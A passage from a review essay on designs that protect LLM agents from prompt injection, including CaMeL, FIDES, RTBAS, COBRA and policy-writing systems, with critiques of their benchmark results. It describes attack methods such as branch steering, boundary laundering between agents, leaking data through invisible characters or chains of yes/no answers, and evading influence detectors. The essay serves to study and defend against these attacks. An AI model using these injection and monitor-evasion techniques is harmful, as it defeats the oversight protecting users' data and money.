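Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, argue that general-purpose agents built on current language models are unlikely to provide reliable safety guarantees. They recommend building agents for particular applications and giving up some abilities. Once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger an action with harmful side effects. They describe six design patterns for achieving this, including Dual LLM and code-then-execute,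 of which CaMeL is an example.

| Pattern | What it forbids | Tasks it rules out | What an attacker can still do |
|---|---|---|---|
| Action-selector | The model chooses from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results | Requests that the developers didn't foresee, and anything that requires reading a result | Nothing through the results |
| Plan-then-execute | Tool results can't add or change actions | Tasks in which the next action depends on what an earlier one finds | Change the content of a planned action, such as the text of an email |
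| Map-reduce | A separate model without tools reads each document and returns only a restricted answer, such as yes or no | Tasks that don't divide into separate documents | Get a false answer about the attacker's own document |
| Dual LLM | The planner never reads untrusted text | Tasks whose instructions are in that text | Falsify what the reader returns |
| Code-then-execute | Untrusted text can't change the program | Tasks with turns that the program doesn't provide for | Falsify values, unless a policy checks them |
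| Context minimisation | The model no longer sees the user's request when it writes the reply | Replies that depend on details the system has deleted | Inject instructions through retrieved data |

Context minimisation mainly defends against direct injection. For instance, if a customer tries to talk a car dealer's chatbot into a discount, the system turns the request into a database query and deletes the customer's words before the model writes its answer.

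Beurer-Kellner and colleagues expect a fixed plan to make an email assistant only slightly less useful, because the choice and order of its actions should rarely depend on what strangers write. They also point out that even with a fixed plan, if the user asks for a reply to an attacker's email, an injection can make the assistant hide confidential information in the reply using invisible characters.

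A coding agent would lose much more of its usefulness. In the safest design they consider, the reader converts outside documentation into a strict list of functions, for example with names of at most 30 characters. An injection is unlikely to survive that conversion, but the conversion also removes the explanations and sample code that make documentation useful. The agent also couldn't follow the installation steps in a README, because the planner would never see them.

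### Tasks that nobody can plan in advance

In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) argue that AgentDojo's tasks mostly fail to expose this drawback. For example, an agent told to pay the bill in a certain file can plan to read the file and send the money from the request alone. By their count, only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan along the way, so they wrote 60 tasks in shopping, code management and daily life that all do.

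With CaMeL, none of the four models in the main comparison completed any of the 60 tasks. Without a defence, the three commercial models completed 52–60% of them. No attack succeeded against CaMeL either, but that is weak evidence of security because the agent never finished a task.

The zero is less surprising given that every task in the benchmark breaks CaMeL's central assumption. Li and colleagues also told the agents to finish without asking the user for confirmation, which may have hindered CaMeL because it asks the user in doubtful cases. DRIFT, a more flexible design, starts from a plan but lets a validator approve departures from it. With the three commercial models, it completed 30–37% of the tasks and let through 0.8–3.1% of the attacks.

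Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest that people rarely give agents such tasks for email, while Li and colleagues believe that open-ended tasks are increasingly common. The shares of 6 in 97 and 60 in 60 don't estimate how common these tasks are in ordinary use, because they reflect what each benchmark's designers wanted to test.

The hardest case is a request to do whatever a document says. In AgentDojo, one user task is to read a file and follow its instructions. *The LLMbda Calculus* describes how CaMeL's planner, unable to see the file, wrote a loop that had the reader interpret each instruction and then called the matching tool. With policies off, this gave the attacker the control that the split was meant to prevent. The earlier CaMeL paper reports a similar problem in its own tests and places it outside its threat model, because the user had told the agent to obey the document. The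 only other attack counted as successful in those tests was a scoring error, triggered when the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word.

### Planning for a screen the planner can't see

This approach seems especially hard to apply to computer-use agents, which look at screenshots and operate a mouse and keyboard, because a planner that can't see the screen doesn't know whether a cookie banner is covering the button it needs. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) had the planner write one long program that covers the situations it might meet. Before an action, a quarantined vision model describes the screen. Another model call checks the description against what the program expects by answering a yes-or-no question, such as "Am I on the login page?", and the program takes the matching branch.

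Plans averaged 4.9 tool calls and 3.7 branches on AgentDojo, compared with 41.1 calls and 39.7 branches on OSWorld, a benchmark of ordinary computer tasks. About half of each plan consisted of fallbacks that didn't run.

Foerster and colleagues report that the design retains up to 57% of a frontier model's performance. Judging by the reported success rates, this figure is based on 109 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had solved without the isolation. The isolated version solved 31 of them (28%) on the first attempt and 62 (57%) in at least one of five attempts. The extra attempts help a user only if something can identify the successful one, and a failed attempt may already have changed files.

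The reported 19% improvement for UI-TARS, a small open model, compares three attempts with a baseline that appears to have had one. On a single attempt, the isolated version did slightly worse, at 22.0% against 24.4% for the baseline, if both figures include the 30 tasks that OSWorld passes by default.

The many branches create a new weakness, which Foerster and colleagues call branch steering. For example, an attacker puts a fake cookie banner inside an advertisement. The plan already includes a step for closing cookie banners, so when the vision model finds the fake one, the agent clicks on it and lands on the attacker's site. The attacker has only chosen among actions already in the plan. The payment program would have the same weakness if it asked the reader whether each invoice was due and paid only if the answer was yes. Branch steering resembles the side channel in reverse, because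 the branch lets untrusted data control an action instead of letting a secret leak out.

Foerster and colleagues tried comparing the screenshot with the page's underlying code and using a second model to confirm what the first one saw. The code comparison caught the fake banner in one advertising format but not in another. The second model had difficulty distinguishing fake banners from real ones without blocking legitimate actions.

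#### Limiting what each branch may do

Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks*, accept that an attacker may influence a branch, so they limit what the branch can do. Their system, COBRA, assigns each branch its permitted destinations, tools and field values before the agent sees any untrusted content. A modified version of ceLLMate then checks the resulting web requests.

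On the COBRA team's own benchmark of 101 tasks, attacks succeeded 89.5% of the time against a plain Dual LLM agent and never against COBRA. When there were no attacks, COBRA kept 97% of the plain Dual LLM agent's utility. That figure leaves out any utility the plain Dual LLM agent had already lost compared with an undefended agent, and Foerster and colleagues had already shown how large the loss from isolation can be.

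The benchmark counts an attack as successful when a harmful action violates the limits in force at that point. A harmful action that the limits permit would apparently not count, so the benchmark is a much better test of whether COBRA enforces its limits than of whether those limits are strict enough.

COBRA's strictest protection also needs a description of each site's operations, with details such as the address and fields of a request to approve a loan. The user must approve this description and reapprove it whenever it changes. Without it, COBRA can restrict only which sites the agent contacts, and that restriction has the same weaknesses as other domain lists.

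COBRA would stop case B if the planner marked the account number as security-critical. COBRA accepts a security-critical value from the user's request or from a source the plan authorises. Otherwise, it asks the user for the value before the task begins.

#### Letting the planner see part of the screen

*Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* (Seip, Markovinović and Hein, 2026) describes SA-CUA, a system that lets the planner see the screen with the untrusted parts masked, so it can decide what to do as it goes. SA-CUA first masks the whole page or document, then uncovers the parts that fixed rules identify as controlled by the site operator, along with a few harmless kinds of content such as prices and dates. The rules rely on the accessibility tree, a structured description of what is on the screen. If a rule is missing, the planner sees less than it could, but the attacker gains nothing.

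Some tasks still need a value from a masked area. Suppose the user wants a Python package that prints coloured text, and a forum post recommends `termcolor`. A component that has not seen this name works out the expected answer from trusted sources, which can include the planner's own knowledge. Ordinary code then compares that answer with the name in the post, and the planner receives the name only if they match. Seip and colleagues call this endorsement. An attacker can make the check fail but can't use the masked text to argue for a different value.

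With the model Qwen3.8-27B, SA-CUA completed 86.2% of the tasks on one benchmark, compared with 18.5% for the design by Foerster and colleagues, and no attack on SA-CUA succeeded. The result depends on the user listing trusted websites and contacts in advance, and on nobody taking them over.

In case B, endorsement would mean checking the account number against the supplier file. Endorsement can confirm only information already in a trusted source, so it would also reject a genuine new number.

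### When one agent instructs another

Larger systems often have one agent that delegates work to others. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) shows that protecting each agent with CaMeL does not protect the whole system. The researchers asked a coordinating agent to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. A second agent fetched the applicants' details from a database, and a third sent messages. The researchers had planted an instruction in the database to email the details to an outsider.

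The first two agents behaved correctly because the planted text never reached their planners. But the coordinating agent's program inserted the summary into the instruction it sent the third agent. That agent treats instructions from the coordinator as its user's request, so its planner read the attacker's order and added a line that sent the email. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering, because untrusted data becomes trusted as it passes from one agent to the next. They ran CaMeL without policies in these tests, and a policy restricting recipients might have stopped the email.

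The proposed solution, multi-CaMeL, gives agents separate channels for instructions and data. On a version of AgentDojo with several agents, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent, and never with multi-CaMeL. Multi-CaMeL therefore adds very little protection on this benchmark, and the constructed example is better evidence of the problem than these averages. Multi-CaMeL also lowers utility, though only modestly with the strongest models.

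### What developers have to build

Developers can put Progent in front of an existing agent as a proxy. CaMeL requires developers to rewrite the agent, according to Narisetty and colleagues. The program has to run in CaMeL's interpreter, and the planner has to know in advance what each tool does and what kind of answer it returns. CaMeL's developers acknowledge that users have to write and maintain the policies. Willison, who has worked on application security for two decades, says even he finds such policies hard.

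The number of tokens an agent uses also depends on whether it calls the planner once or at every step. Foerster and colleagues tried both. Their CaMeL version, which calls the planner once, used 1.88 times as many tokens as the undefended agent. A version based on FIDES, a related design that calls the planner again before each action, used 29.6 times as many tokens as the undefended agent and solved about the same number of tasks as the CaMeL version within five attempts.

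Policies written for one set of tools may not fit another. *AutoDojo* tests several defences on AgentDyn but leaves out CaMeL because it would have needed extensive policies for each of the benchmark's three simulated settings.

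## Can labels follow influence through a model's reasoning?

CaMeL can tag every value with its origin because its planner writes a program, and an interpreter can track each value through it line by line. Most agents have no such program. Their model reads one long prompt and produces the next tool call, and nothing in the call shows which email or file led to it. To use labels on such an agent, a designer has to decide which label to give the model's output.

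### Two rules from the 1970s

Information-flow control labels data by origin and secrecy, carries the labels along as a system uses the data, and blocks any flow that violates its rules. The two classical rules cover secrecy and integrity. Under the secrecy rule, secret data must not reach an output that people without clearance can read. Under the integrity rule, which Kenneth Biba formulated, untrusted data must not determine anything that the system trusts. In the office assistant, the secrecy rule would keep the contract from an outsider, and the integrity rule would keep a stranger's email from causing a payment.

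When a system combines two pieces of data, the result's secrecy and integrity labels are at least as strict as those of either piece. A secrecy label can be a list of permitted readers. If Ana and Ben may read one document, and Ben and Carla another, only Ben may read a text derived from both. An integrity label can list everyone who might have written part of the data, so the combined label includes everyone on either list.

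*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) applies both rules to agents. In ordinary code, a programmer can see that `c = a + b` depends only on `a` and `b`. But any word in a model's prompt may have affected any word of its answer, and a programmer can't see which ones did. The safe choice is to give each answer the combined label of everything the model has read.

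### Three tool calls later

Suppose the owner gives the office assistant a supplier's address and asks it to summarize the current status, then write a note telling the supplier that Tuesday works. The assistant makes three calls before it writes anything.

| Tool call | Label of the result | Label of whatever the assistant writes next |
|---|---|---|
| Fetch the company's published payment terms | Trusted; anyone may read | Trusted; anyone may read |
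| Open the contract | Trusted; owner and lawyer may read | Trusted; owner and lawyer may read |
| Open the supplier's latest email | Untrusted; owner and supplier may read | Untrusted; only the owner may read |

The assistant now writes "Tuesday suits us" to the supplier. The secrecy rule blocks the note because the assistant has read the contract, which the supplier may not read. The integrity rule also blocks it, because an instruction in the supplier's email might have caused it. The note contains nothing from either document, but its label depends on what the model has read. The assistant can't write to the lawyer either, because the lawyer may read the contract but not the supplier's email. Further reading can only make the label stricter, so the assistant can't send anything for the rest of the session.

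Researchers call this label creep, and it makes agents less useful. When Costa and colleagues applied such labels and policies to an ordinary agent running GPT-4o, its utility fell from 98.8% to 37.5% on AgentDojo's banking tasks and from 93.3% to 20.0% on the Slack tasks.

### FIDES hides the text

Costa and colleagues at Microsoft propose a planner called FIDES, which avoids reading data that would taint its label. It builds on Willison's split between a planner and a quarantined reader.

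1. A tool returns a result in which each field has its own label.
2. FIDES compares these labels with the planner's current one. If a field would make the planner's label stricter, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. The other fields stay visible.
3. The planner can pass a variable to a tool unread, or have an isolated model extract something from it into a new variable.
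4. The planner can also open a variable, but it then takes on the variable's label.
5. Before each tool call, ordinary code checks the labels against a policy.

For actions with serious consequences, the policy can require that the planner chose the call in a trusted state and that every argument is trusted. For tools that send data, everyone who will receive an argument must be among its permitted readers. A policy can also set different rules for different arguments, for example by requiring a trusted recipient but allowing the body of a message to come from a web search.

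In the supplier example, the contract and the email would stay in variables. The isolated model would write the summary for the owner, and the planner could still send the note about Tuesday without having read either document.

With its policies on, FIDES let no attack in AgentDojo through, compared with 152 successful attacks on an undefended agent. AgentDojo's own scoring recorded three successes against FIDES, which Costa and colleagues discounted after inspecting them by hand. One reason they give for discounting an attack is that the policy allowed the action, such as posting a Slack message without a link. The zero therefore means that no attack broke the policy, though an attacker could still have got the agent to do something the policy allowed. The labels were also better than a company could expect to have, because the researchers marked a field as untrusted if at least one of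 AgentDojo's attacks targets it. Nobody has a list of the fields that attacks will target in a real mailbox.

FIDES completed 8 percentage points more tasks than an ordinary agent under the same kind of policies, and 16 points more when both used OpenAI's reasoning model o1. For someone deciding whether to install FIDES, the more relevant comparison is with an undefended agent. Averaged over the four settings, GPT-4o completed about 84% of tasks undefended and 50% with FIDES and its policies. Some of this loss is deliberate, because several banking tasks tell the agent to follow instructions in a file, which the policies are meant to prevent. Most of the rest comes from GPT-4o mishandling the variables, which o1 handled better.

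### RTBAS masks what a step doesn't need

*RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) observes that a model reads its whole history at every step but usually needs only a little of it. Before each step, a screener selects the parts of the history that seem relevant. RTBAS combines the labels of those parts and masks everything with a stricter label than the combined one. The model then chooses a tool call. If the policy forbids that call under the combined label, the user has to confirm it.

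Because RTBAS masks whatever the screener judges irrelevant, its security doesn't depend on the screener being right. If the screener wrongly dismisses a hostile email as irrelevant, RTBAS hides the email from the model, so the email can't influence the call. The screener's mistakes lead instead to missing information or unnecessary questions. This matters because the screeners can be unreliable. One is a language model that names the relevant passages, and the other is a small neural network that uses attention data and was right only 81% of the time in testing.

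On AgentDojo, RTBAS blocked every attack that violated its policy. The 2% loss in utility reported in the abstract applies when the agent is under attack. Without an attack, the loss was 10% with the language-model screener and 7.4% with the attention-based one. Utility fell most on the Slack tasks, where the agent completed only 22% and 33% with the two screeners, respectively, because many of these tasks involve reading a website and acting on it. The tests had no user to confirm calls, so RTBAS skipped every call it would have asked about. Utility could be higher with a user present.

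In 37 further tasks involving private data, RTBAS required an unnecessary confirmation in 8% or 16% of cases, depending on the screener, compared with 30% for an agent that requires confirmation before every call. RTBAS roughly doubled the time and cost of a banking task.

### Controlled exceptions

Since labels only get stricter, a useful system needs a way to relax them. Relaxing a secrecy label is called declassification, and treating untrusted data as trusted is called endorsement.

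An owner who tells the assistant to send the contract to a new outside lawyer is asking for declassification. A policy can allow this if no untrusted text influenced the decision to send, a condition known in the theory as robust declassification. When the condition holds, a secrecy violation is presumably what the owner wanted.

FIDES can base endorsement partly on how much information an answer can carry. Suppose the user wants a calendar event if any of three emails asks for a meeting. The isolated model reads the emails and returns only yes or no to the planner. A one-bit answer is too small to contain an injection, so a policy may let the planner act on it. Costa and colleagues left these restricted answers out of their AgentDojo tests because few tasks needed them, so FIDES's results provide no evidence of how safe the exception is.

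Yes-or-no answers still call for caution, because a single one can determine a whole decision, such as whether to pay an invoice, and several together can carry much more information. In the labelling scheme that Costa and colleagues describe, combining two yes-or-no answers gives the same label as one. Thirty answers could therefore encode any number up to a billion, a range that covers many account numbers, without making the label any stricter. A policy would also have to count the questions.

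### Influence that leaves no words behind

An assistant's owner has told it to delete files once nobody needs them. It reads an email mentioning that the auditors have finished with last year's invoices, and calls the delete tool on a folder named `2025`. The assistant would not have made the call without the email. This influence is implicit because none of the email's words appear in the call, so a scanner that compares the two would find no match.

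Strict labels cover this case because every call the planner makes after reading the email counts as untrusted, whether or not the email had any effect. For secrets, FIDES guarantees only that the data doesn't flow directly into a public output, so side channels like those in CaMeL remain open. Costa and colleagues consider a stronger guarantee impractical because it would essentially forbid any publicly visible call after the agent had read a secret.

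Labelling therefore relies on assumed influence, without measuring it. In *Ghost in the Agent*, Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026) try to measure influence with NeuroTaint, which analyses an agent's log afterwards. NeuroTaint first reconstructs where each piece of outside text entered and where it went. If the agent saved any of this text to memory, NeuroTaint saves the label with it, so the text's origin can still be traced in a later session. For each sensitive call, it then searches the arguments for traces of the outside text, from exact copies to passages with a similar meaning.

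If NeuroTaint finds none, it runs a counterfactual test. It replaces the suspect text with something neutral, such as "No relevant information found," and gives a language model both versions of the history. That model judges whether the agent would still have made the same call. If not, NeuroTaint reports that the text influenced the call.

In the prompt they print, Cai and colleagues ask the judge to predict what the agent would have done, without rerunning the agent. Their evidence is therefore one model's prediction about another. In their leading example of implicit influence, a poisoned search result makes an agent send its research to an attacker's web address. The influence is less purely implicit than they claim, because that address appears in both the search result and the agent's call.

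No existing benchmark labelled this kind of influence, so Cai and colleagues built TaintBench, which has 400 scenarios in 20 agent frameworks. Outside text influences a sensitive call in 200 of the scenarios. NeuroTaint found 187 of these and wrongly flagged 16 of the other 200. It found 37 of the 40 cases that needed the counterfactual test. A detector based on FIDES found 108 of the influenced scenarios and raised 106 false alarms, but this is little evidence about FIDES itself, which is designed to block calls in advance. The comparison reduced it to a rule that largely treats any path from an outside source to a sensitive tool as influence. NeuroTaint and the FIDES-based detector did almost equally well on two older benchmarks of unsafe actions.

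The audit takes only about a quarter of a second per unit of execution, and its counterfactual queries averaged only 457 tokens. But like ADR, it works too late to stop a theft. NeuroTaint's recall also fell to 55% when Claude Opus 4.6 replaced GPT-4.1 mini as the agent. At least part of the drop occurred because the stronger model resisted some attacks that the benchmark still counts as influence.

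### Reading the model's attention

In *What Guides the Agent?*, Gao, Zhang and colleagues (2026) look for influence inside the model. As a model produces each token, its attention weights determine how much each earlier token contributes to the computation. Their system, AttnLocate, averages the weights that connect a tool call to the outside text in the prompt, giving most importance to layers about two-thirds of the way through the model. A small neural network then searches for a stretch of text with the pattern typical of an instruction the model is following. A separate rule checks whether the source of that stretch is authorized to cause the call.

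Across ten agent configurations, AttnLocate caught an average of 93.4% of hijacked calls, with false alarms on 6.7% of the rest. Unlike NeuroTaint, it can flag a call before it takes effect, and it shows which sentence was responsible. But it needs access to the model's internals, so only the model's provider or a company that hosts its own model can use it. The tests used open models, mostly with 7 to 14 billion parameters, and the main results come from a detector trained separately for each model and benchmark.

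Long contexts are a bigger worry. The detection rate fell from 97% for contexts of up to 256 tokens to 86% for those above 2,048, and a working agent's prompt can be many times longer than that. AttnLocate also examines only the attention from the final call, leaving out the model's written reasoning. An email that influenced the call through that reasoning might therefore receive little direct attention. This didn't seem to hurt in the tests, where AttnLocate located instructions slightly better in the Qwen3 models when reasoning was switched on.

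### An attacker who knows the method

FIDES and RTBAS can offer a guarantee against an adaptive attacker, because rewording a text doesn't help the attacker if the model chooses its action without reading that text. The guarantee holds only if the labels and policy are right and the tools handle the labels correctly. Zhong and colleagues describe an agent with one tool that may send private data and another that returns sent messages as public data. If the user sends themselves a private message, it comes back labeled public. Every exception, such as letting the planner see a yes-or-no answer, gives the attacker back a little influence.

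NeuroTaint and AttnLocate offer no comparable guarantee, and neither main evaluation includes an attacker who knows the method. NeuroTaint's judge reads the hostile text, so an attacker could include an argument that the call was routine and would have happened anyway. An attacker might also plant the same order in two emails. NeuroTaint removes one source at a time, and the remaining email would still cause the call, so the judge could answer correctly about each email and still miss the attack.

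An attacker with a copy of the model that AttnLocate protects could keep rewording an injection until the agent obeyed it and the attention pattern no longer revealed it. Nobody has shown that either evasion works, but Nasr and colleagues beat other detectors with a similar search. Until someone tests these evasions, the two methods are better suited to investigating incidents than to deciding which actions an agent may take.

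### Who sets the first label?

The guarantees of FIDES and RTBAS depend on labels that someone has to assign before the agent reads anything. By default, FIDES treats the user's messages as trusted and public. If the user pastes a stranger's email into the chat and adds "please deal with this", FIDES gives the email the same trusted label as the user's own words. If the email is confidential, the "public" label is also wrong.

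The one attack that got past RTBAS in AgentDojo succeeded for a similar reason. The system labelled a text as trusted because it attributed the text to the user, but the text contained a possible injection. Zhong and colleagues acknowledge that the security guarantees are "only as good as the labels provided".

RTBAS can give parts of one message different labels, so a chat program that recorded which text the owner had pasted could mark that text as untrusted. The pasted email would then not carry the owner's authority. But the assistant would have very little guidance, because its only trusted instruction would be to deal with an email it isn't allowed to act on.

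Different parts of an incoming email need different labels. Costa and colleagues suggest that the sender's address could be trusted if the mail server has authenticated it, while the body stays untrusted. They also mention marking a document as trusted once an injection classifier has cleared it, but warn that relying on such classifiers could weaken the guarantees. Attackers have evaded these classifiers, and a single missed injection would remove the protection for that document.

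Even a number can be wrongly labeled as trusted. In one AgentDojo task, the user wants a new password if the account shows a suspicious transaction. FIDES labeled the transaction descriptions untrusted and hid them from the planner, but it labeled the amounts and dates trusted and showed them. The planner found one amount suspiciously high and changed the password. Costa and colleagues correctly count this as consistent with the policy. But whoever makes a payment chooses its amount, so if strangers can pay into the account, they can influence the decision through a field labeled trusted.

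### Three kinds of integrity

In May 2026, Qu and colleagues proposed a definition of what a secure agent would have to achieve. Three of its conditions concern untrusted data. (A fourth, tool integrity, requires that third-party tools do nothing beyond what they declare.)

| Property | What it requires | What can enforce it | Where that falls short |
|---|---|---|---|
| Instruction integrity | Every action traces back to the user's instruction, or to content the user told the agent to follow | Keeping untrusted text away from the planner | Tasks in which the next step depends on what the agent reads |
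| Data-flow integrity | Data goes only where its origin and secrecy allow, including in later sessions | Labels, and a policy for each tool | Someone has to write those policies, which is impractical for large collections of tools |
| Judgment integrity | A decision stays the same when an attacker adds content that has no bearing on the right answer | No method with a guarantee | The agent has to read the untrusted data to make the decision |

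Qu and colleagues rate CaMeL as fully enforcing the first two properties and not enforcing the third at all. Case B shows how an attack can succeed without violating the first two. The owner asked for the payment, and passing an account number from an email to the bank is an allowed flow unless the payment policy requires a trusted account number. But the assistant is wrong about which account belongs to the supplier.

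Tool calls and their arguments are structured objects that a monitor can label or separate from untrusted data. Qu and colleagues point out that a judgment, by contrast, depends on the data itself, because the data is the evidence. Another problem is that their condition applies to additions that don't change the right answer, so enforcing it requires knowing that answer, which can't be determined from the text of a bank notice.

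Labels can help here because they add information that isn't in the text. A notice from an authenticated address that the supplier has used for years deserves more weight than one from a domain registered last week. But if the attacker writes from the supplier's real mailbox, the labels will also match those on a genuine notice.

A designer can enforce a limit on what the agent's judgment may cause. Under a strict integrity rule, an account number from an email can't select the payee, however convincing the email is. This in effect takes the decision away from the agent, which works well for payments because a supplier file can hold the correct account. An agent that reviews papers or compares products has no such file, since the user asked for its judgment. A designer can restrict its output to a score from one to five so that the output can't contain a stolen contract, but an attacker can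 still try to persuade the agent to give a five.

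## Who writes the policy, and who approves what it leaves open?

Progent, CaMeL and FIDES all enforce rules that someone has to supply. If a rule lets the office assistant send files to any address, a monitor working as designed will still allow the theft in case A. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* acknowledges that enforcing a policy does not establish that the policy captures what the user and the company meant, and that checking this remains an open research problem.

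### Why an agent's policy is hard to write

Android's makers defined a list of permissions for phone apps, each app's developer picks the ones the app needs, and the user sees them at installation. This works tolerably well because most apps do the same few things every day. By contrast, an agent's owner types a new task each time, in ordinary language, and the task may change while the agent works on it, so the right permissions change too.

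The wording of policies is also a problem. A monitor needs rules written in a language with an exact meaning, about a known set of actions, such as "the recipient's address must be in the supplier file". Real policies contain rules like "do not share sensitive data", and no formal policy language can express "sensitive". A price list, for example, may be secret in March and on the company's website in April. Somebody has to replace the word with something a program can test, such as a folder or a label, and the replacement will sometimes be wrong.

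A language model can judge what is "sensitive" without a definition, but if it were the monitor, attackers could search for its mistakes. Several designs instead have a model write the rules beforehand and ordinary code enforce them.

### Rules fixed in advance

The oldest method is for an administrator to write the rules once. Gemini CLI, Google's command-line coding agent, supports this. According to Google's *Policy engine*, each rule names a tool, optionally with a pattern for its arguments, and one of three decisions: allow, deny or ask the user. The matching rule with the highest priority wins, and an administrator's rules always outrank the user's. If a rule denies a tool outright, the program doesn't show that tool to the model. By default, the agent can generally read files but has to ask before it changes one or runs a shell command.

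People can inspect such rules, and a hostile email can't change them. But the rules stay the same whatever the task is. In *Contextual Agent Security*, Tsai and Bagdasarian (2025) tested two fixed policies on an agent with 20 file and email tasks, such as emailing a backup of important files. Without a policy, the agent completed 14.0 tasks on average. A policy that blocked every action that changes something reduced this to zero, because every task required a change. With a policy that allowed everything except deletion, the agent completed 12.2 tasks, but the policy didn't stop inappropriate actions, such as obeying an email that said to forward all messages about urgent security flaws.

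### Rules that a model writes for each task

Tsai and Bagdasarian's own system, Conseca, writes a new policy for every request:

1. The user states a task. A policy model, separate from the agent, receives the task, the tools' documentation and some "trusted context" that the developer has selected. In the prototype, this includes email addresses and the names of files and folders, but not the contents of emails or files.
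2. The policy model lists the commands that the agent may use for this task, with a pattern for each argument and a sentence explaining the rule. The developer can have the user approve the list before the agent starts.
3. Ordinary code compares each command with the list. If it refuses a command, the agent receives the explanation and can try something else.

With Conseca, the agent completed 12.0 of the 20 tasks, about as many as with the permissive fixed policy. Conseca also blocked the agent from forwarding the security emails in every task except one, where the user had told the agent to do whatever urgent emails asked. The same kind of request was also a problem for CaMeL and Kairos. The result is preliminary, as Tsai and Bagdasarian say. They planted a single email, used a model that is now long out of date, and did not test Conseca against an attacker who knew about it.

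The policy model never reads what the agent finds, so an attacker can't use an email to argue for a looser rule, as he can try to do with Progent. But the model then has to predict from the user's request which actions the task will need, and it can't do that if the user says "carry out the tasks in my manager's email".

A plausible rule can also allow what it should block and block what it should allow. For the task of answering urgent work emails, the example policy in the paper requires a recipient at `work.com` and the word "urgent" in the subject line. As printed, the pattern matches `@work.com` anywhere in the address, so `bob@work.com.example.net`, an address on somebody else's domain, would pass. A legitimate reply headed "Re: server down" would fail. Tsai and Bagdasarian suggest a simpler rule language for future versions. The trusted context can't be fully trusted either. If the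 agent saves an attachment under the name its sender gave it, the policy model receives a stranger's words as a trusted file name.

*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) criticises Conseca for assuming that the policy model is safe, and notes that a hijacked planner may find a way around the policy. Any monitor has this second weakness, because an attacker can use whatever actions its rules allow. The reliance on a safe policy model is more specific to Conseca, which writes new rules for each request. A good policy for one request is therefore only weak evidence that the next will be good, and nobody reviews the new policy unless the user does.

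### Rules translated from prose and then checked

Another approach is to have a model translate a written policy into a formal language, then check the translation before relying on it. Several projects use Cedar, an open-source policy language from Amazon Web Services (AWS), because software can compare two Cedar policies over every possible request instead of a sample.

Vatsa, Shome and colleagues (2026), in *AutoCedar*, illustrate their method with a musician who shares an album through a web app. Members of her band and the producer may download tracks, but nobody may download a track under embargo. Before it writes a policy, AutoCedar turns these sentences into two kinds of limit. A floor contains requests that the policy must allow, and a ceiling contains all the requests that it is free to allow. If S(P) is the set of requests of a given type that a policy P permits, the finished policy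 must satisfy

S(floor) ⊆ S(P) ⊆ S(ceiling)

AutoCedar calculates these limits from small pieces. A reviewer, either a person or another model, sees each piece next to the sentence it came from and approves it. A model then writes the policy, and Cedar's tools look for a request that breaks a limit. If they find one, the model gets it back as a counterexample and tries again.

In 178 of 200 cases (89%), AutoCedar's policy permitted exactly the same requests as an independently prepared reference policy. When the same model wrote the policy directly, it matched the reference in 132 cases (66%). The cases come from general access control rather than agents, and an error rate of one in nine is high for something meant to give a guarantee. But the comparison is good evidence that the reviewed limits help.

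*VeriGuard* (2025) generates policy code for agents and verifies that it meets formal conditions, but both the code and the conditions come from the same plain-language request. If both contain the same misinterpretation of that request, the code will satisfy the conditions and still be wrong.

### Grounding, checkability and synthesis

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* defines the ideal as the prose and the formal policy agreeing on whether to allow each action in every situation the system can reach. Nobody can check this directly, because the prose is ambiguous. The paper divides what remains into three open problems.

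Grounding means deciding what the words refer to in the actual system. In the album example, a developer could represent "band member" as a role attached to each user, but then a member of any band could download the album. AutoCedar's model instead linked each track to its album, the album to its band, and the band to its members. Vatsa and colleagues point out that no later check can catch the role-based reading, because all later checks use the same vocabulary. The office assistant has a similar problem with "the supplier's account", which could mean the number in the supplier file or the number in the supplier's latest email. Under the second reading, the false notice in case B satisfies a fully verified policy.

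Checkability is how reliably anyone can tell whether the policy matches the prose, once the words have a fixed meaning. Mondl, Maisel and Brock (2026), in *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code*, describe their output as formally verified. A program checks the syntax, the references to tools, and whether any rules contradict each other or can never apply, but a second language model judges whether a rule means the same as its source. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* asks whether restricting how people phrase policies and which formal rules they may use could make that judgement reliable enough to support a guarantee.

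Synthesis is the translation of prose into a policy. A translator should come with a limit on how far its policy can stray from the prose, and it should be able to revise the policy as the task develops. Without such a limit, a policy may be far too strict and still look like a success. Mondl and colleagues translated an 88-rule policy for an agent that handles medical records, added some rules from an existing server, and replayed recorded runs against the result. The rules blocked 94–100% of runs in which the agent tried to change a record, including runs on ordinary tasks with no attacker.

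Many of those blocks may be correct. The two rules that fired most often, 416 times each, require the agent to restate the patient's identity and to get confirmation before a change. A live agent, unlike a recording, could have asked and then carried on. But Mondl and colleagues, who work for a company that develops such controls, measured how much of the policy the rules covered, not whether the agent could still do its job, so the figures would look much the same if the policy forbade every change.

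### Cruder rules in the meantime

Until translation improves, developers can use rules about the agent as a whole. One is to avoid Willison's "lethal trifecta" of private data, hostile text and a way to send data out. Under Meta's similar Agents Rule of Two, from October 2025, an agent should have at most two of three properties within one session: it processes untrustworthy input, it has access to private data or sensitive systems, or it can change things or communicate with the outside. If a task needs all three, a person has to supervise. Meta's third property is wider than Willison's, since it covers deleting a file or making a payment as well as sending data.

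A developer can apply either rule by checking the agent's list of tools, without anticipating each task. The office assistant has all three properties. A company could split it into one agent that summarises mail and can't send anything, and another that pays invoices from the supplier file and never reads mail. That would stop both test emails, but the owner could no longer tell a single assistant to go through the mail and pay whatever is due, which was the reason for having an assistant.

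Critics object that two of the properties can be enough for an attack. Willison describes an attack by Håkon Måløy on Copilot in Microsoft Word. Hidden text in a source document makes Copilot alter the document the user is writing and copy the hidden text into it, so the new document can infect others. The attacker can falsify a company's documents without receiving any data, so removing the outside connection would not prevent this. Microsoft had 144 days to respond before publication, but Willison reports no mitigation that covers the whole class of attack.

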